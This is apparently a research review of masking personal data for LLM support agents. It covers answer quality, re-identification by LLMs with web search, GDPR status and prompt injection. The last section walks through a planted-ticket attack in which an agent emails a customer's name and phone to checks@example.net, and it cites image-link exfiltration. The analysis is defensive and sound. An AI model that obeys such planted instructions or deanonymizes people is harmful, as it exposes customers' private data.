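The last task is the closest to a support agent that searches old complaints, and all five models lost at least 22 percentage points on it. The number of masked values doesn't explain the drop, because the long reasoning texts also contained many of them and GPT-4o mini's score on those texts didn't change.

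Some of the errors came from masking information that wasn't personal. In a question about solar eclipses, the software replaced "Earth" and "Sun" with placeholders for locations, and the model chose the wrong answer. In another question, it masked two exchange rates, $1.36 and $1.40, and the model concluded that the euro had fallen when it had risen. Software that masked only names and contact details would not have changed either question, so these results probably overstate how many errors such software would cause.

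Numbered placeholders worked much better than replacing every hidden value with the same label. On the long reasoning texts, GPT-4o mini scored 0.70 with numbered placeholders and 0.52 with the single label. Telling the model that the text was anonymised made no consistent difference.

Masking can also improve an answer. After the agency in *RAGAL* masked its old support cases, its assistant stopped copying details from them into new replies and instead wrote templates with gaps to fill. Someone asking for technical help needs the procedure from an old case but not the name of the person who had the problem.

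### Which details the model needs

How much masking harms an answer therefore depends on whether the hidden value affects that answer. In *Semantically-Aware LLM Agent to Enhance Privacy in Conversational AI Services*, Serenari and Lee (2025) had three students judge this for 1,195 names, places and organisations in 866 real ChatGPT prompts. They marked a detail as relevant if replacing it would change the meaning of the prompt or noticeably affect the answer.

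By majority vote, 748 of the details were relevant, including 267 of 290 cities and countries but only 228 of 591 people's names. Someone who asks for the population of Chicago needs an answer about Chicago, but a stern email to an employee called Jessica can be addressed to Kate, and software can then change the name back.

Serenari and Lee trained a small model, LOPSIDED, to replace only irrelevant details. It replaced details the answer needed about a fifth as often as Hide-and-Seek, a system that tries to replace everything. But it missed 8% of the details it should have replaced, compared with 3% for Hide-and-Seek. That 8% doesn't include relevant details, which made up 63% of all details in this sample and which LOPSIDED sends to the main model's provider on purpose.

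Deciding what is relevant can also go wrong. In one of Serenari and Lee's examples, a user asks about the weather in Palo Alto. The software replaces "Palo Alto" with "San Jose" before sending the question to the model, then changes the name back in the answer. The user receives San Jose's weather labeled as Palo Alto's. The cities are close, so the answer may be nearly right, but the user can't tell that it is for a different city.

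*PromptPET* (Yang, Iqbal and colleagues, 2026) measured how much removing sensitive details harms a chatbot's answers, using 2,182 real queries. The paper is concerned with advertising profiles, so it protects interests and circumstances as well as identifiers. A model scored each sensitive detail for its importance to the answer. Removing high-scoring details harmed the answers about four times as much as removing the same number of low-scoring ones.

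They compared four ways of changing every sensitive detail. In the table, privacy measures how much the change disrupted the profile a model could infer from the query, and utility measures how closely the answer matched the original one. Both scores run from 0 to 1. The last column gives the share of queries that scored well on privacy but poorly on utility.

| Change | Privacy | Utility | Protected, but with a poor answer |
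|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0.21 | 0.90 | 0.4% |
| Remove the detail | 0.59 | 0.63 | 25.2% |
| Make it more general | 0.70 | 0.65 | 25.4% |
| Replace it with another | 0.62 | 0.67 | 24.2% |
| Keep it and add a decoy | 0.77 | 0.76 | 7.4% |

The decoy method adds a second request. If a user asks for a therapist, the software also asks for a dentist, then deletes the dentist from the answer. This makes it harder to build an accurate profile of the user, but it can't hide a phone number, because the real value is still in the text. It would also be risky in an agent, which might act on the decoy request. PromptPET uses learned rules to choose a method for each detail, and it uses decoys for 85% of them. It uses removal mainly for details that contribute little to the answer, such as passwords and identifiers pasted into code.

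Removing a detail can have a different effect from replacing it. Liu, Xie and colleagues (2026), in *Demystifying the Privacy-Utility Trade-off in LLM Interactions*, took 384 prompts with five sensitive statements each and removed or replaced one statement at a time. A second model scored the answers. The effect of removal also depended on the kind of information. When the user wanted a specific task carried out, removing information about relationships lowered the score by 14.25 points, while removing health information raised it by 0.19. For example, a request to arrange a family dinner depends on who is in the family, but probably not on an old knee injury.

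For those same tasks, replacing health information with invented details scored 14.04 points worse than leaving it out, because the model treated the invented details as true. In conversations where users wanted sympathy or personal support, inventing a health detail scored slightly better than leaving it out. The direction of the large effects is more informative than their exact size, because the scoring model's points have no natural unit and the 384 prompts, spread over six kinds of request and seven kinds of information, include few examples of some combinations.

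Liu and colleagues then trained a small model, Veilmind-4B, to decide whether to keep, remove or replace each statement. When set to favour useful answers, it produced responses at least as good as the originals for 86.8% of prompts. When set to favour privacy, it still left 40.5% of the sensitive statements in the text. It kept some of those because it classified them as necessary for the request, but it also failed to detect more than a quarter of the sensitive statements.

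For the support agent, these results favour masking contact details, which the agent usually just passes from one tool to another, and leaving most of the complaint unmasked.

### The case for masking only the logs

Some developers think masking text on its way to the model is a mistake. WiLine's *Mask Your Logs, Not Your Prompts* argues that the model should read the real text and that software should mask only the copies a company stores. WiLine's own platform can host a gateway set up this way. WiLine says a model can't tell three people apart if all of them have become [REDACTED], and may refuse a request when "social security number" appears beside a meaningless code. It adds that a tool may reject a placeholder, and the agent then wastes time retrying.

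*RedacBench* (Jeon, Kim and Shin, 2026) is the main research behind the argument. It tests how well models remove sensitive information from 514 essays and emails, using 187 confidentiality policies. It breaks each text into separate facts and checks which ones a reader can still infer after redaction. WiLine quotes the result for GPT-5 mini, which removed 80.9% of the sensitive facts but kept only 37.6% of the harmless ones.

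That result comes from a method in which the model rewrites each text twice to satisfy policies that can be as broad as keeping all strategic business information confidential. Replacing a phone number with [PHONE_1] is a much smaller change. When Jeon and colleagues just masked words and phrases, 73–85% of the harmless facts remained, though only 36–52% of the sensitive ones were removed. They also measured what remained in the text, not whether a model could still do a task with it. The drop from 0.80 to 0.32 that Deußer and colleagues reported would be better evidence for WiLine's position.

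Providers charge less when the beginning of a prompt exactly matches an earlier one. If Maria Lopez is [NAME_1] throughout a session, the masked text begins the same way each time and the discount still applies. WiLine also argues that masking breaks the match, but that is true only if the placeholders change from call to call.

The larger objection to masking only the logs is that the model's provider still receives every name and number. WiLine argues that data leaks from storage, not from the model reading it, but the provider may store prompts too, and the shop can't mask the provider's logs. WiLine concedes that a provider's retention policy is a separate question. Masking only the logs is reasonable for a shop that runs the model on its own servers, since no outside company reads the text. A shop that uses a hosted model has to either rely on the provider's promises about storage or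 mask at least the values the model doesn't need.

### Tests on agents that use tools

Nearly all of this evidence comes from single questions, letters and summaries. An agent has to carry a placeholder through several tool calls, and a mistake in one call can ruin the steps after it. Few published tests measure how often that happens.

The closest tests of whether an agent still does its job with masking involve agents that operate a phone or computer through its screen. *PrivacyGuard* (2026) replaces personal data before a hosted model sees it and restores the real values on the device when the agent acts. In 16 runs on a Xiaomi phone, the software never crashed and the agent completed its task 14 times. With so few runs, the true success rate could be anywhere from about 62% to 98%, and the count alone doesn't show how many tasks the agent would have completed without masking.

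*GUIGuard-Bench* (2026) tested an agent on AndroidWorld, a set of tasks on Android phones, with and without private information masked in every screenshot. The agent completed fewer tasks with masking. Letting it see the private details that a task required recovered some of the loss, but not all. As a compromise, the paper suggests masking whatever the task doesn't need and substituting realistic values for the rest.

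Screens also contain personal data that text placeholders can't cover. *CAPED* (2026) points out that an earlier placeholder system for phone agents protects text but not contact photos, personal pictures or the thumbnails of recommended videos.

Tests with ordinary tool calls mostly examine what the agent sends out. In a trial of 307 live calls, Li's software for trimming arguments cut its own measure of privacy exposure by 81–92%, and every call remained valid. But the models had already read the real values, so the trial doesn't show how well an agent works without seeing them.

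## Can people be identified after their names, emails and phone numbers are removed?

Suppose the shop's masking software hides every name, email address and phone number. Maria Lopez's ticket would still give her away as the only vet in her village. Few customers stand out that much, but more ordinary details can have the same effect. This is a masked message from another customer:

> [NAME_1] here. My refund still hasn't arrived. I live in Elmsworth and teach chemistry, and I could do with the money because last month's flood wrecked my car. Please write to [EMAIL_1].

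The table follows the details through a country of 50 million adults. The town and the counts are invented.

| What the reader knows | Adults who fit |
|---|---|
| Nothing yet | 50,000,000 |
| Lives in Elmsworth | 20,000 |
| Also teaches chemistry | 8 |
| Also lost a car in last month's flood | 1 |

Thousands of people in the country teach chemistry, and no single detail in the message identifies anyone. To identify the person from the combined details, a reader needs other sources. If the local school's website lists its science teachers and the newspaper interviewed one of them beside a ruined car, two searches would be enough.

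Researchers have known for decades that people can be identified after their names and contact details are removed. Lermen, Paleka and colleagues (2026), in *Large-scale online deanonymization with LLMs*, cite an estimate that postcode, birth date and gender together single out 87% of Americans. They argue that most people who wrote under a pseudonym were safe only because identifying them took a skilled investigator hours, and that language models have removed this protection.

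### What a model can infer from masked text

Attribute inference means working out a personal fact that a text doesn't state. For example, someone who complains about a particular tram line has probably revealed their city. In 2023, Staab and colleagues showed that language models could infer location, occupation and income from people's writing with high accuracy. According to Lermen and colleagues, the models relied on clues that a skilled human would also notice, but cost far less. A later system, AutoProfiler, divided the job among four agents and extracted such attributes with 85–92% accuracy.

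Knowing someone's job and city is still some way from knowing who they are. Krčo, Yao and colleagues (2026), in *RAT-Bench*, measure that gap by estimating how many Americans share the facts an attacker recovers. Their benchmark works like this:

1. The researchers draw a profile from US census survey data. It has five quasi-identifiers from a list of nine, such as date of birth, state and occupation. They keep only profiles that would identify the right person with a probability above 90%, and add one invented direct identifier.
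2. GPT-4.1 writes a text containing those details, such as a conversation with a doctor. It states them plainly, writes them in an unusual form or only implies the quasi-identifiers.
3. A masking tool processes the text.
4. GPT-4.1, now acting as the attacker, tries to recover the details. It is told which kinds of fact to look for.
5. If the attacker recovers the direct identifier, the person counts as re-identified. Otherwise, a statistical model estimates the chance that the recovered facts point to the right person, and anything above 20% counts. That corresponds to hiding among fewer than five people.

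The table gives the share of people re-identified, based on 100 profiles. Azure is Microsoft's commercial masking service.

| Tool | Details stated plainly | Details in an unusual form | Details only implied |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 98% | 32% |
| Azure | 22% | 33% | 21% |
| GPT-4.1 with Anthropic's PII purifier prompt | 26% | 58% | 19% |
| Presidio | 41% | 77% | 30% |
| Average of all tools tested | 44% | 69% | 28% |

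Azure's figures were low partly because it deleted a lot of harmless text. The tools barely helped with implied details, because there was no word or number for them to find.

Some of these failures came from direct identifiers that the tools missed, especially those in an unusual form. When direct identifiers were written plainly, the tools caught most of them, and the remaining risk came mainly from quasi-identifiers. Krčo and colleagues also tested texts with no direct identifiers at all. As the number of quasi-identifiers rose from three to nine, the re-identification rate rose for every tool, reaching 60% for Presidio.

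The benchmark shows why recall can mislead: it gives a missed gender the same weight as a missed date of birth, although gender rules out only about half the population. But the benchmark probably overstates the risk in an average ticket, because the researchers chose identifiable people and had the model mention the revealing details. It also counts people as re-identified if the facts statistically single them out, without requiring anyone to find their names.

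### Finding the person's name

Lermen and colleagues tested whether an AI agent with web search could identify 338 users of Hacker News, a technology forum, who had linked their accounts to their LinkedIn profiles. They gave the agent a summary of each person's posts, removing names, usernames and identifying links but keeping employers, interests and demographic details. The agent was right about 226 people (67%) and wrong about 25, and each attempt cost between $1 and $4.

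In a second test, the attacker had 987 LinkedIn profiles and had to find each person's account among about 89,000 on Hacker News. A model summarised everyone's posts, software selected the 100 accounts most similar to each profile, and two further models picked a candidate and checked it. When the researchers allowed at most one wrong guess in 100, the system found 45.1% of the accounts. A method adapted from a 2008 attack on anonymous film ratings found 0.1%.

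In that test, the right account was always in the pool, which a real attacker couldn't count on. People who openly link their accounts also probably reveal more about themselves than people who want to stay anonymous. Lermen and colleagues acknowledge that this could inflate the success rates.

People are easier to identify when there is more of their text to compare. In a test that matched Reddit users by the films they discussed, the system found 3.1% of those whose two sets of posts had one film in common and 48.1% of those with ten or more, at a precision of 90%. The same risk arises when a support agent remembers old tickets. Using the same placeholder for a customer across tickets helps the agent recognise them when they return, but it also links their details into one profile.

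People can sometimes be identified even after a careful publisher redacts the data. Anthropic released interviews with 125 scientists after removing some identifying details. In *Agentic LLMs as Powerful Deanonymizers*, Li (2026) used ordinary agents with web search to link six of 24 interviews to specific published works. Lermen and colleagues' agent named nine of 33 scientists correctly and two wrongly, although the researchers had to judge for themselves whether the matches were correct. Scientists are easier to find than most customers because they publish detailed descriptions of their work.

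In the test closest to masking, Ko, Jeong and colleagues (*From Weak Cues to Real Identities*, 2026) replaced names, email addresses and file paths in 30 ChatGPT conversations with placeholders and gave the conversations to an agent with web search. The agent correctly named one person, a member of the researchers' own group, by combining a rough location, a research topic, a job and the timing of events. Most of the other conversations revealed only a broad description of the person. The researchers had picked these 30 from 1,916 sessions because they contained private matters, so the result shows that masked chats can identify someone, but not how often they do.

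An agent may also identify someone when nobody has asked it to. Ko and colleagues gave models two tables of ten records each, with one person in both, and asked an ordinary business question, such as whether customers who write reviews spend more. Claude 4.5 picked out the shared person in 77% of cases and GPT-5 in 13%. An instruction to protect privacy lowered those rates to 7% and 0%, but average task scores also fell, from 0.97 to 0.92 for Claude and from 0.87 to 0.77 for GPT-5. When the user named a target to look for, the instruction again nearly eliminated the matches, but Claude's task score fell from 0.99 to 0.45 because it also refused legitimate work. Both models are now old, and newer ones might handle the instruction better.

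### Making details more general

The simplest remedy is to replace a precise detail with a vaguer one. The software could change "I live in Elmsworth and teach chemistry" to "I live in the north and work as a teacher". If the north has 5 million adults and one in 100 is a teacher, 50,000 people fit. But if one in 10,000 of them lost a car in last month's flood, that detail narrows the group to five. Five just passes RAT-Bench's threshold, but someone could still identify the person from a newspaper report. The software would have to replace the mention of the flood too, perhaps with "an unexpected expense".

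None of these changes affects the answer about the refund, but the model would need the real town to answer a question about the nearest place to return a parcel. In the PromptPET tests described earlier, making details more general spoiled many answers.

### Rewriting the message

A language model can rewrite the whole message, so it can deal with hints as well as individual words. Staab and colleagues later developed a version in which one model tries to infer personal facts from the text, another rewrites the passages that revealed them, and the process repeats.

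Krčo and colleagues found that the results depended on what the system was told to hide. When it was given the benchmark's exact list of facts, the rate of re-identification from plainly stated details fell to 2%. The rate was 44% with five of those facts, chosen at random, and 56% with the general list of data types that Presidio uses. The shop can't list every revealing detail in advance, and might think of jobs and towns but not of a wrecked car.

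Rewriting also takes more computing power than masking and loses the customer's own words, which may matter if a complaint turns into a dispute. The shop would have to run the rewriting model itself to avoid sending the original complaint to an outside company.

### Adding calibrated noise

Differential privacy is a mathematical way to limit what anyone can learn from an output. A random procedure *M* satisfies it if, for any two possible inputs *x* and *x*′ and any output *y*,

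Pr[*M*(*x*) = *y*] ≤ *e*^ε · Pr[*M*(*x*′) = *y*]

No output can be more than *e*^ε times as likely to come from one input as from another. A smaller ε means more noise and stronger privacy.

Batan Arachchige, Asghar and colleagues (2026), in *Protecting User Prompts via Character-Level Differential Privacy*, apply this to each character of a prompt. Their software either keeps a character or swaps it for one of 93 others, and it keeps the character with probability

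*e*^ε ÷ (*e*^ε + 93)

At ε = 4.53, each character has a one-half chance of being replaced. The model then repairs the damaged text from context. In the paper's example, it recovers "correspondence" from "cbrr/MpondenXe" but can't recover the name "Harlan". In tests on medical records and company emails, models recovered personal data about as rarely as they would recover random strings. The software doesn't have to detect personal data first, so detection errors can't expose any of it.

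However, the formal guarantee weakens with each character. For a ten-digit phone number at ε = 4.53, the same output can be up to 93¹⁰ (about 5 × 10¹⁹) times as likely for one original number as for another. At that setting, a phone number is protected mainly because half its digits are probably wrong and the model has no context for correcting them. The same kind of errors would make order numbers unusable to an agent.

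The method does little for quasi-identifiers, because it relies on the model restoring common words. The model would probably restore "teach", "chemistry" and "flood", which are the revealing part of the message. More noise would hide those words too, but it might make the complaint unintelligible to the model.

Another kind of noise swaps whole words for similar ones. When Krčo and colleagues tested one such method, TEM, the attacker still re-identified 88% of people whose details appeared explicitly, compared with 99% when the text was unchanged. Even a successful swap can reveal personal information. If the software replaces one diabetes drug with another, the reader still learns that the customer probably has diabetes.

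### Can one method suit every use?

In *Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs* (2026), Ganesh, More and colleagues argue that no single method can protect every kind of prompt. They reviewed 31 research papers and 11 publicly available tools. More than three-quarters of the papers proposed a method for all uses of language models, and more than half didn't discuss its limitations. All 11 tools were for general chatbot use.

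They want a method to protect data, preserve the quality of answers, run efficiently, adapt to different fields and be easy to use, and they see three conflicts among these aims:

- Stronger protection removes information that a useful answer may need, and reducing that loss takes more computing.
- Noise and encryption offer mathematical guarantees about numbers or characters, but people care about meaning. Two prompts can be close by a mathematical measure and reveal very different things.
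- A tool that adapts to medicine, law and casual email needs a user who understands the privacy risks in each. A tool that anyone can use without thinking can't adapt in this way.

The evidence for the first conflict is strong. Generalising, rewriting and adding noise all lost something useful, and Deußer and colleagues found that masking badly damaged answers drawn from retrieved documents. But a trade-off doesn't prove that a good compromise is impossible. Computing on encrypted text, for example, could in principle protect a prompt without changing the answer. Ganesh and colleagues reject it for large models because it is too slow and expensive, though its speed and cost could change.

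The third conflict depends on the user having to supply the context. Software such as PromptPET and Veilmind-4B can assess each detail automatically, so one tool can be both adaptable and easy to use. Ganesh and colleagues answer this objection only briefly, by referring to another paper. But Veilmind-4B left many sensitive statements in place even when set to favour privacy, so automatic assessment doesn't yet solve the problem.

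The research therefore supports the narrower conclusion that no fixed treatment suits every message. Ganesh and colleagues accept that simple masking can be good enough for someone who wants help with casual emails. They also warn that an imperfect tool may be worse than none if it encourages people to share more, but they don't measure how often that happens. They mainly advise building and testing privacy controls for one application at a time. This suits the shop, which knows that most refund questions don't depend on the customer's job, town or car.

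### Is masked text still personal data?

The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main data protection law, applies to information about an identified or identifiable person, but not to anonymous data. Data is pseudonymised when nobody can link it to a person without additional information that is kept separately and protected. A ticket with placeholders is pseudonymised if the mapping table is secure and the rest of the text doesn't reveal who wrote it.

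Under the law, a controller decides why and how to use personal data, and a processor handles it on the controller's behalf. The shop is a controller. A company that runs a model for the shop is a processor if it uses the tickets only as the shop instructs.

In January 2025, the European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together the EU's data protection regulators, took the view that pseudonymised data remains personal data if someone could use additional information to link it to a person (SCL, *EDPB adopts pseudonymisation guidelines and provides guidance on cooperation with competition authorities*, 2025).

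The EU's Court of Justice (CJEU) took a different view that September in *European Data Protection Supervisor v Single Resolution Board* (2025), or EDPS v SRB. The case arose from the failure of a Spanish bank. The Single Resolution Board (SRB), an EU body that deals with failing banks, collected comments from the bank's shareholders and creditors and passed 1,104 of them to the consultancy Deloitte. Each comment had a random code, and only the SRB could link the codes to the commenters. Some commenters complained that the SRB hadn't told them Deloitte would receive their comments.

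The case concerned a regulation for EU institutions, but the Court interprets its definitions in the same way as the GDPR's. It reached three main conclusions:

- A personal opinion relates to the person who expressed it. A customer's complaint would presumably count as well.
- Pseudonymised data isn't personal data for everyone in all cases. It may not be personal for a recipient that can't undo the pseudonymisation and can't identify people in other ways, including by cross-checking with other information.
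- The duty to tell people who will receive their data depends on the controller's position when it collects the data. The SRB could identify the authors, so it had to tell them about Deloitte even if Deloitte couldn't identify anyone.

The Court sent the case back to the lower court, so it didn't finally settle whether Deloitte had received personal data.

The most relevant guidance for a company that masks data before sending it to a model provider is the EDPB's *Guidelines 02/2026 on Anonymisation*, a draft from July 2026. Under the draft, data that is personal for the controller is also personal for a processor working on the controller's behalf. Otherwise, a company could escape the law by outsourcing its work. In one example, an online retailer sends extracts from its customer records to an agency for analysis. Because the retailer can identify the customers, the extracts are personal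 data for the agency too.

The shop is in the same position. It holds the mapping table, so under the draft, masked tickets are personal data for both the shop and a provider that acts as its processor. The shop still needs a data-processing contract with the provider, and it must tell customers which companies, or at least what kinds of companies, receive their data. The rules on sending data outside the EU also apply. Masking counts in the shop's favour as a security measure, since a leak at the provider would expose fewer names and numbers.

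If the provider also uses the tickets for its own purposes, such as training a new model, the draft's reasoning suggests that the test becomes whether the provider itself could identify the customers. VBB's *Anonymisation Key Takeaways from the EDPB's Draft Guidelines* (2026) explains that the risk of identification needs to be insignificant, not zero, and that a contractual promise not to identify people carries less weight than a legal ban. A provider with web search could probably identify the chemistry teacher from Elmsworth, so that ticket would probably be personal data for the provider even without the mapping table.

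The guidelines are still a draft, and the public consultation ends on 30 October 2026, according to Inside Privacy's *EDPB publishes draft guidelines on anonymisation* (2026). The GDPR itself may also change. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed the Digital Omnibus, which would rewrite the definition of personal data to reflect the Court's ruling. The EDPB and the European Data Protection Supervisor, which oversees EU institutions, objected to the new definition in February 2026, according to the National Law Review.

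Member state governments have also resisted it. White reports in *EU member states finalize negotiating stance on Digital Omnibus* that they agreed in October 2026 to keep the existing definition and add standards for pseudonymisation. They now have to negotiate with the European Parliament, so the shop should plan around the current definition.

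## What does masking protect when the model is manipulated?

A contract can limit what the company that runs the model does with the shop's tickets, but it does not bind a stranger who writes a ticket to make the agent send customers' details elsewhere. Most masking systems are built to keep data from the company. Whether they also keep it from the stranger depends largely on where the client puts the real values back.

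### The curious provider

*Veil-Then-Reveal* (Elmahallawy, Shaaban and Carroll, 2026) describes the adversary that most masking systems assume, which security researchers call "honest but curious". The provider runs the model correctly and doesn't tamper with its work, but it may read, store and analyse every prompt and reply, compare sessions and bring in outside information. It can't break into the user's device, which holds the keys and the mapping table.

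Their system runs on the user's device and is well suited to this adversary. It encrypts a phone number or card number into another number of the same format, which the device can decrypt with a key. For names, places, organisations and email addresses, it uses realistic substitutes and a mapping table, as SurrogateShield does. The keys change with each session, so the same customer gets different substitutes each time and the provider can't link sessions by matching them. The software discards the keys and the table when the session ends.

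In tests by Elmahallawy and colleagues, 27.0% of the personal values in 664 prompts from the PUPA dataset still reached the model with protection, compared with 95.1% without it. On 1,000 documents from another dataset, 2.9% did. Nearly all of what got through was data the detector had missed. The researchers limit their guarantee to data the detector finds, and their tests exclude tool calls.

That exclusion matters for agents because an agent's reply may be a tool call, in which case the model determines who receives the restored values. In a chat, the restored reply goes to the person who supplied the data, so it reveals nothing new.

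### The outsider

Unlike the provider, a stranger who plants text in a ticket can't read the prompts or the replies, but writes part of what the model reads and may receive whatever the agent sends out. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) describes the problem: "The agent is authorized; the use is not intended."

Masking hides personal data on the path between the client and the model. Data stolen by an outsider leaves on a different path, from the client through a tool, so a system can hide every phone number from the provider and still send one to a stranger. A rule that lets the agent email only the address on record can prevent that theft, but the provider still reads every unmasked ticket.

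*PAAC* (Yuan, Fang and colleagues, 2026), a system for agents, shows how closely masking designs are tailored to the first adversary. It splits the work between a hosted model, which plans with placeholders, and a small model on the user's device. If someone asks how much money is left after rent, the hosted model can plan to subtract [RENT] from [BALANCE] without seeing either figure. The device then restores the real values in every action before it runs the tools.

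On the retail part of τ²-bench, PAAC completed 57.9% of tasks and had a leak rate of 16.9%. With an ordinary pattern-based detector in place of its own, it completed 35.1% and had a leak rate of 51.5%. The leak rates measure what reached the hosted model. Yuan and colleagues consider whether an attacker can use planted instructions to get extra personal data past the masking and into the cloud, but their measure doesn't cover a real value that the device supplies to the wrong recipient.

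### How agents leaked what they had read

In *Simple Prompt Injection Attacks Can Leak Personal Data Observed by LLM Agents* (June 2025), Alizadeh, Samei and colleagues tested the outsider's attack on agents with no masking. They used the banking part of AgentDojo, which has 11 tools and 16 user tasks. The original benchmark includes some attacks that leak data, but only data held in the tool the attacker controls. The new attacks targeted any data the agent had seen while doing the user's task.

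The planted text was disguised as an important message from the user. It addressed the model by name and told it to email certain details to an outside address before carrying on. These were the account balance and address in one version, a password and one or two other details in two versions, and only the password in a fourth. An attack counted as a success if any sensitive detail got out.

On average, the attacks succeeded about 20% of the time against most of the six models and 40% of the time against Llama 4, but the rates varied widely between the four versions. When the text didn't mention a password, the attack succeeded 93% of the time against Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 55% against Llama 4. When the text asked only for the password, the attack failed every time against every model except Llama 4.

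When the attacker asked for a password and one other detail, the models usually revealed the other detail. GPT-3.5 Turbo revealed the password in 3 of 16 tasks and Llama 4 in 2, while the other models never did. When the request included two other details, more of the models leaked the password. Alizadeh and colleagues attribute the protection of passwords to safety training, which evidently didn't extend to addresses and balances. Such training does little for a shop, whose records consist mostly of addresses and phone numbers.

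They then tried four defences on GPT-4o. Scanning tool results with a trained detector and repeating the user's request after each tool call each cut the attack success rate to 0%. Letting the model keep only the tools it expected to need cut it to 3.1%.

The results were worse on a broader test of 48 tasks, 32 of them synthetic. About 15% of attacks succeeded against the undefended agent, and no defence stopped them all. Repeating the user's request became much less effective. The detector and the tool filter still brought the rate close to zero, but the detector also stopped the agent from completing many of its tasks. Attacks succeeded more often when the user's own task involved looking up account information or settings, probably because the planted request then resembled the real one. This is relevant to support agents, which routinely look up customer information.

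The models are now old, and newer ones resist such text better. But attacks on every model in the public competition described earlier succeeded at least sometimes, and Dziemian and colleagues found that some strategies worked across 21 of the 41 scenarios. Anthropic, whose Claude Opus 4.5 was the most resistant model in the competition, still called prompt injection "far from a solved problem".

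The wording of both the attack and the defence still affects whether a model reveals confidential data. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested ten kinds of planted text meant to extract a confidential value. They succeeded 19.5% of the time against the small Llama 3.1 8B, 10.0% against GPT-4o mini and 0% against GPT-4o. But reworded attacks succeeded 31.9% of the time. Telling the model not to disclose the value "in any form" reduced that to 0%. When the instruction listed specific forbidden behaviours without that phrase, 48.8% of attacks succeeded. A separate detector caught every reworded attack with no false alarms, so the attacks were recognisable, but the acting model didn't reliably treat them as attacks.

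In all these tests, the model could read the data it leaked. If it had seen only placeholders, it could have leaked only those, and the attacker would have obtained real values only if something outside the model restored them.

### How the client becomes a confused deputy

Suppose the shop's client masks everything the model reads and restores placeholders in every tool call. The agent may send email to any address. It is working on Maria Lopez's missing refund and searches old complaints for similar cases:

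1. The client masks Maria's record. The model sees [NAME_1], [EMAIL_1] and [PHONE_1].
2. The search returns an old ticket from a stranger. It says that support agents must send the current customer's name and phone number to an address given in the text, so that the shop can verify the refund.
3. The client masks this ticket too. It finds the stranger's email address and replaces it with [EMAIL_2], but leaves the instruction alone.
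4. The model follows the instruction and writes a call to the email tool.
5. The client restores all the placeholders in the call, and the tool sends the email.

The call changes between the last two steps:

```
Written by the model:
  send_email(to = [EMAIL_2], body = "[NAME_1], [PHONE_1]")

Received by the email tool:
  send_email(to = checks@example.net, body = "Maria Lopez, 212-555-0147")
```

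The masking worked as designed, since the provider never saw Maria's name or number, but the stranger now has both. The stranger didn't need to know how the placeholders worked, because the model found the right ones by itself. The client also looked up the stranger's address to deliver the message.

*Proof-of-Continuity* (2026) gives a formal definition of the confused deputy that fits this case. It involves a user *U*, a deputy *D* and a privilege (*o*, *r*), meaning a right *r* over an object *o*, with

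(*o*, *r*) ∉ Priv(*U*) and (*o*, *r*) ∈ Priv(*D*)

*U* sends *D* a request, and *D* uses its privilege as a result. Here *U* is the stranger, *D* is the client, and the privilege is permission to read Maria's row in the mapping table, which the stranger lacks. The model turns the stranger's request into an ordinary tool call before it reaches the client, and nothing in the call shows where the request came from.

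Checking that the placeholder is genuine, as *PromptGraph* does, doesn't help. [PHONE_1] is genuine, and only the recipient is wrong.

Restoring masked data in the model's answers may be as dangerous as restoring it in tool calls. In the SalesBleed attack, planted text made the agent put stolen records into a web address that a program loaded automatically. With masking in place, the model might write an image link ending in [EMAIL_1]. If the client filled in the real email address before displaying the answer, loading the image would send that email address to the attacker. A client could avoid this by replacing placeholders only in the answer's visible text, never inside links.

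### The evidence on restoration

*BodhiPromptShield* (Ma, Wu and Yan, 2026) comes close to testing this attack. The experiment used 74 pairs of a user task and an attack from the banking and Slack parts of AgentDojo, and every attack tried to send the user's data to an outsider. It compared three agents running on Qwen3 32B, a model with downloadable weights. One had no masking, one had a client that restored masked values for any recipient, and one had a client that restored them only for recipients the user had named.

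| Condition | Attacks that succeeded | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| No masking | 55 of 74 (74.3%) | 62.2% |
| Values restored for any recipient | 51 of 74 (68.9%) | 56.8% |
| Values restored only for recipients the user named | 47 of 74 (63.5%) | 59.5% |

Masking didn't stop the attacks. The three rates are in the order we would expect if limiting restoration helps, but the test is too small to show that it does. The 95% interval for the difference between the first and last rows runs from a fall of 23.0 percentage points to a rise of 1.4.

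The success rate is also a poor measure of how much real data leaked. Ma and colleagues note that the attacker usually obtained a placeholder, not a live identifier, so an attack could count as a success without revealing anyone's details. Only two of the Slack tasks put a protected value into a tool call. The claim that restoring values everywhere is dangerous therefore rests mainly on the argument above about how such a client works, not on a measured rate.

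In another of their tests, agents carried out 200 everyday tasks, such as writing a message based on private notes, with nobody attacking them. The share of exact identifiers that appeared in the final action was 13.7% without masking, 3.1% when a trained detector's placeholders stayed in place, and 11.6% when the software restored the values just before the action. Some recipients were supposed to get the real values, but the result shows that masking followed by restoration changes little about what recipients see.

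Restoring the protected values later exposed far fewer of them to the agent. When the software waited until the tool was about to run, 1.6% of the values were readable in the text it released to the agent, compared with 51.0% when it restored them while the agent was still planning.

An attacker who steals a placeholder also gets the text around it, which can help reveal the missing value. Ma and colleagues gave an attacking model masked documents and asked it to choose each missing value from four candidates of the same kind. Where their best detector had removed the value, the model still chose correctly 64.0% of the time, against 25% for guessing. A real attacker rarely has such a list, but a stranger who received Maria's masked ticket would still get the quasi-identifiers that identify her.

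### Restoring a value only where a rule allows it

The remedy is to treat each restoration as a request that software can refuse. Hidet's *mcp-pvp*, an open-source library for MCP, is built this way. It keeps real values in what it calls a vault and denies every restoration that a policy doesn't explicitly allow. An article on Ready Tensor describes what happens when a tool call arrives with a placeholder in it:

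1. The vault finds the placeholder and notes which tool and which argument it appears in.
2. It checks whether the policy allows that type of data in that argument of that tool. The policy has no wildcard, and no setting can make the model itself a permitted destination.
3. It creates a signed permit for this one disclosure. The permit names the session, the placeholder, the type of data, the tool and the argument, and it expires after five minutes by default.
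4. It verifies the permit, fetches the real value and runs the tool.
5. It scans the tool's result and replaces any personal data there with new placeholders before the model reads it.

The scan in the last step is needed because many tools repeat their input. An email tool might report that it sent a message to Maria's real address, and without the scan the model would receive that address.

The shop could write a policy with a single rule:

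```
send_email    to: email address
refuse everything else
```

In the attack above, the body of the email contains [NAME_1] and [PHONE_1]. No rule allows names or phone numbers there, so the vault doesn't restore them and the stranger doesn't get Maria's number.

The signed permit prevents someone from forging a request or reusing a placeholder in another session. It doesn't stop a manipulated agent that stays within the policy, because the vault itself issues a permit whenever the policy allows the disclosure.

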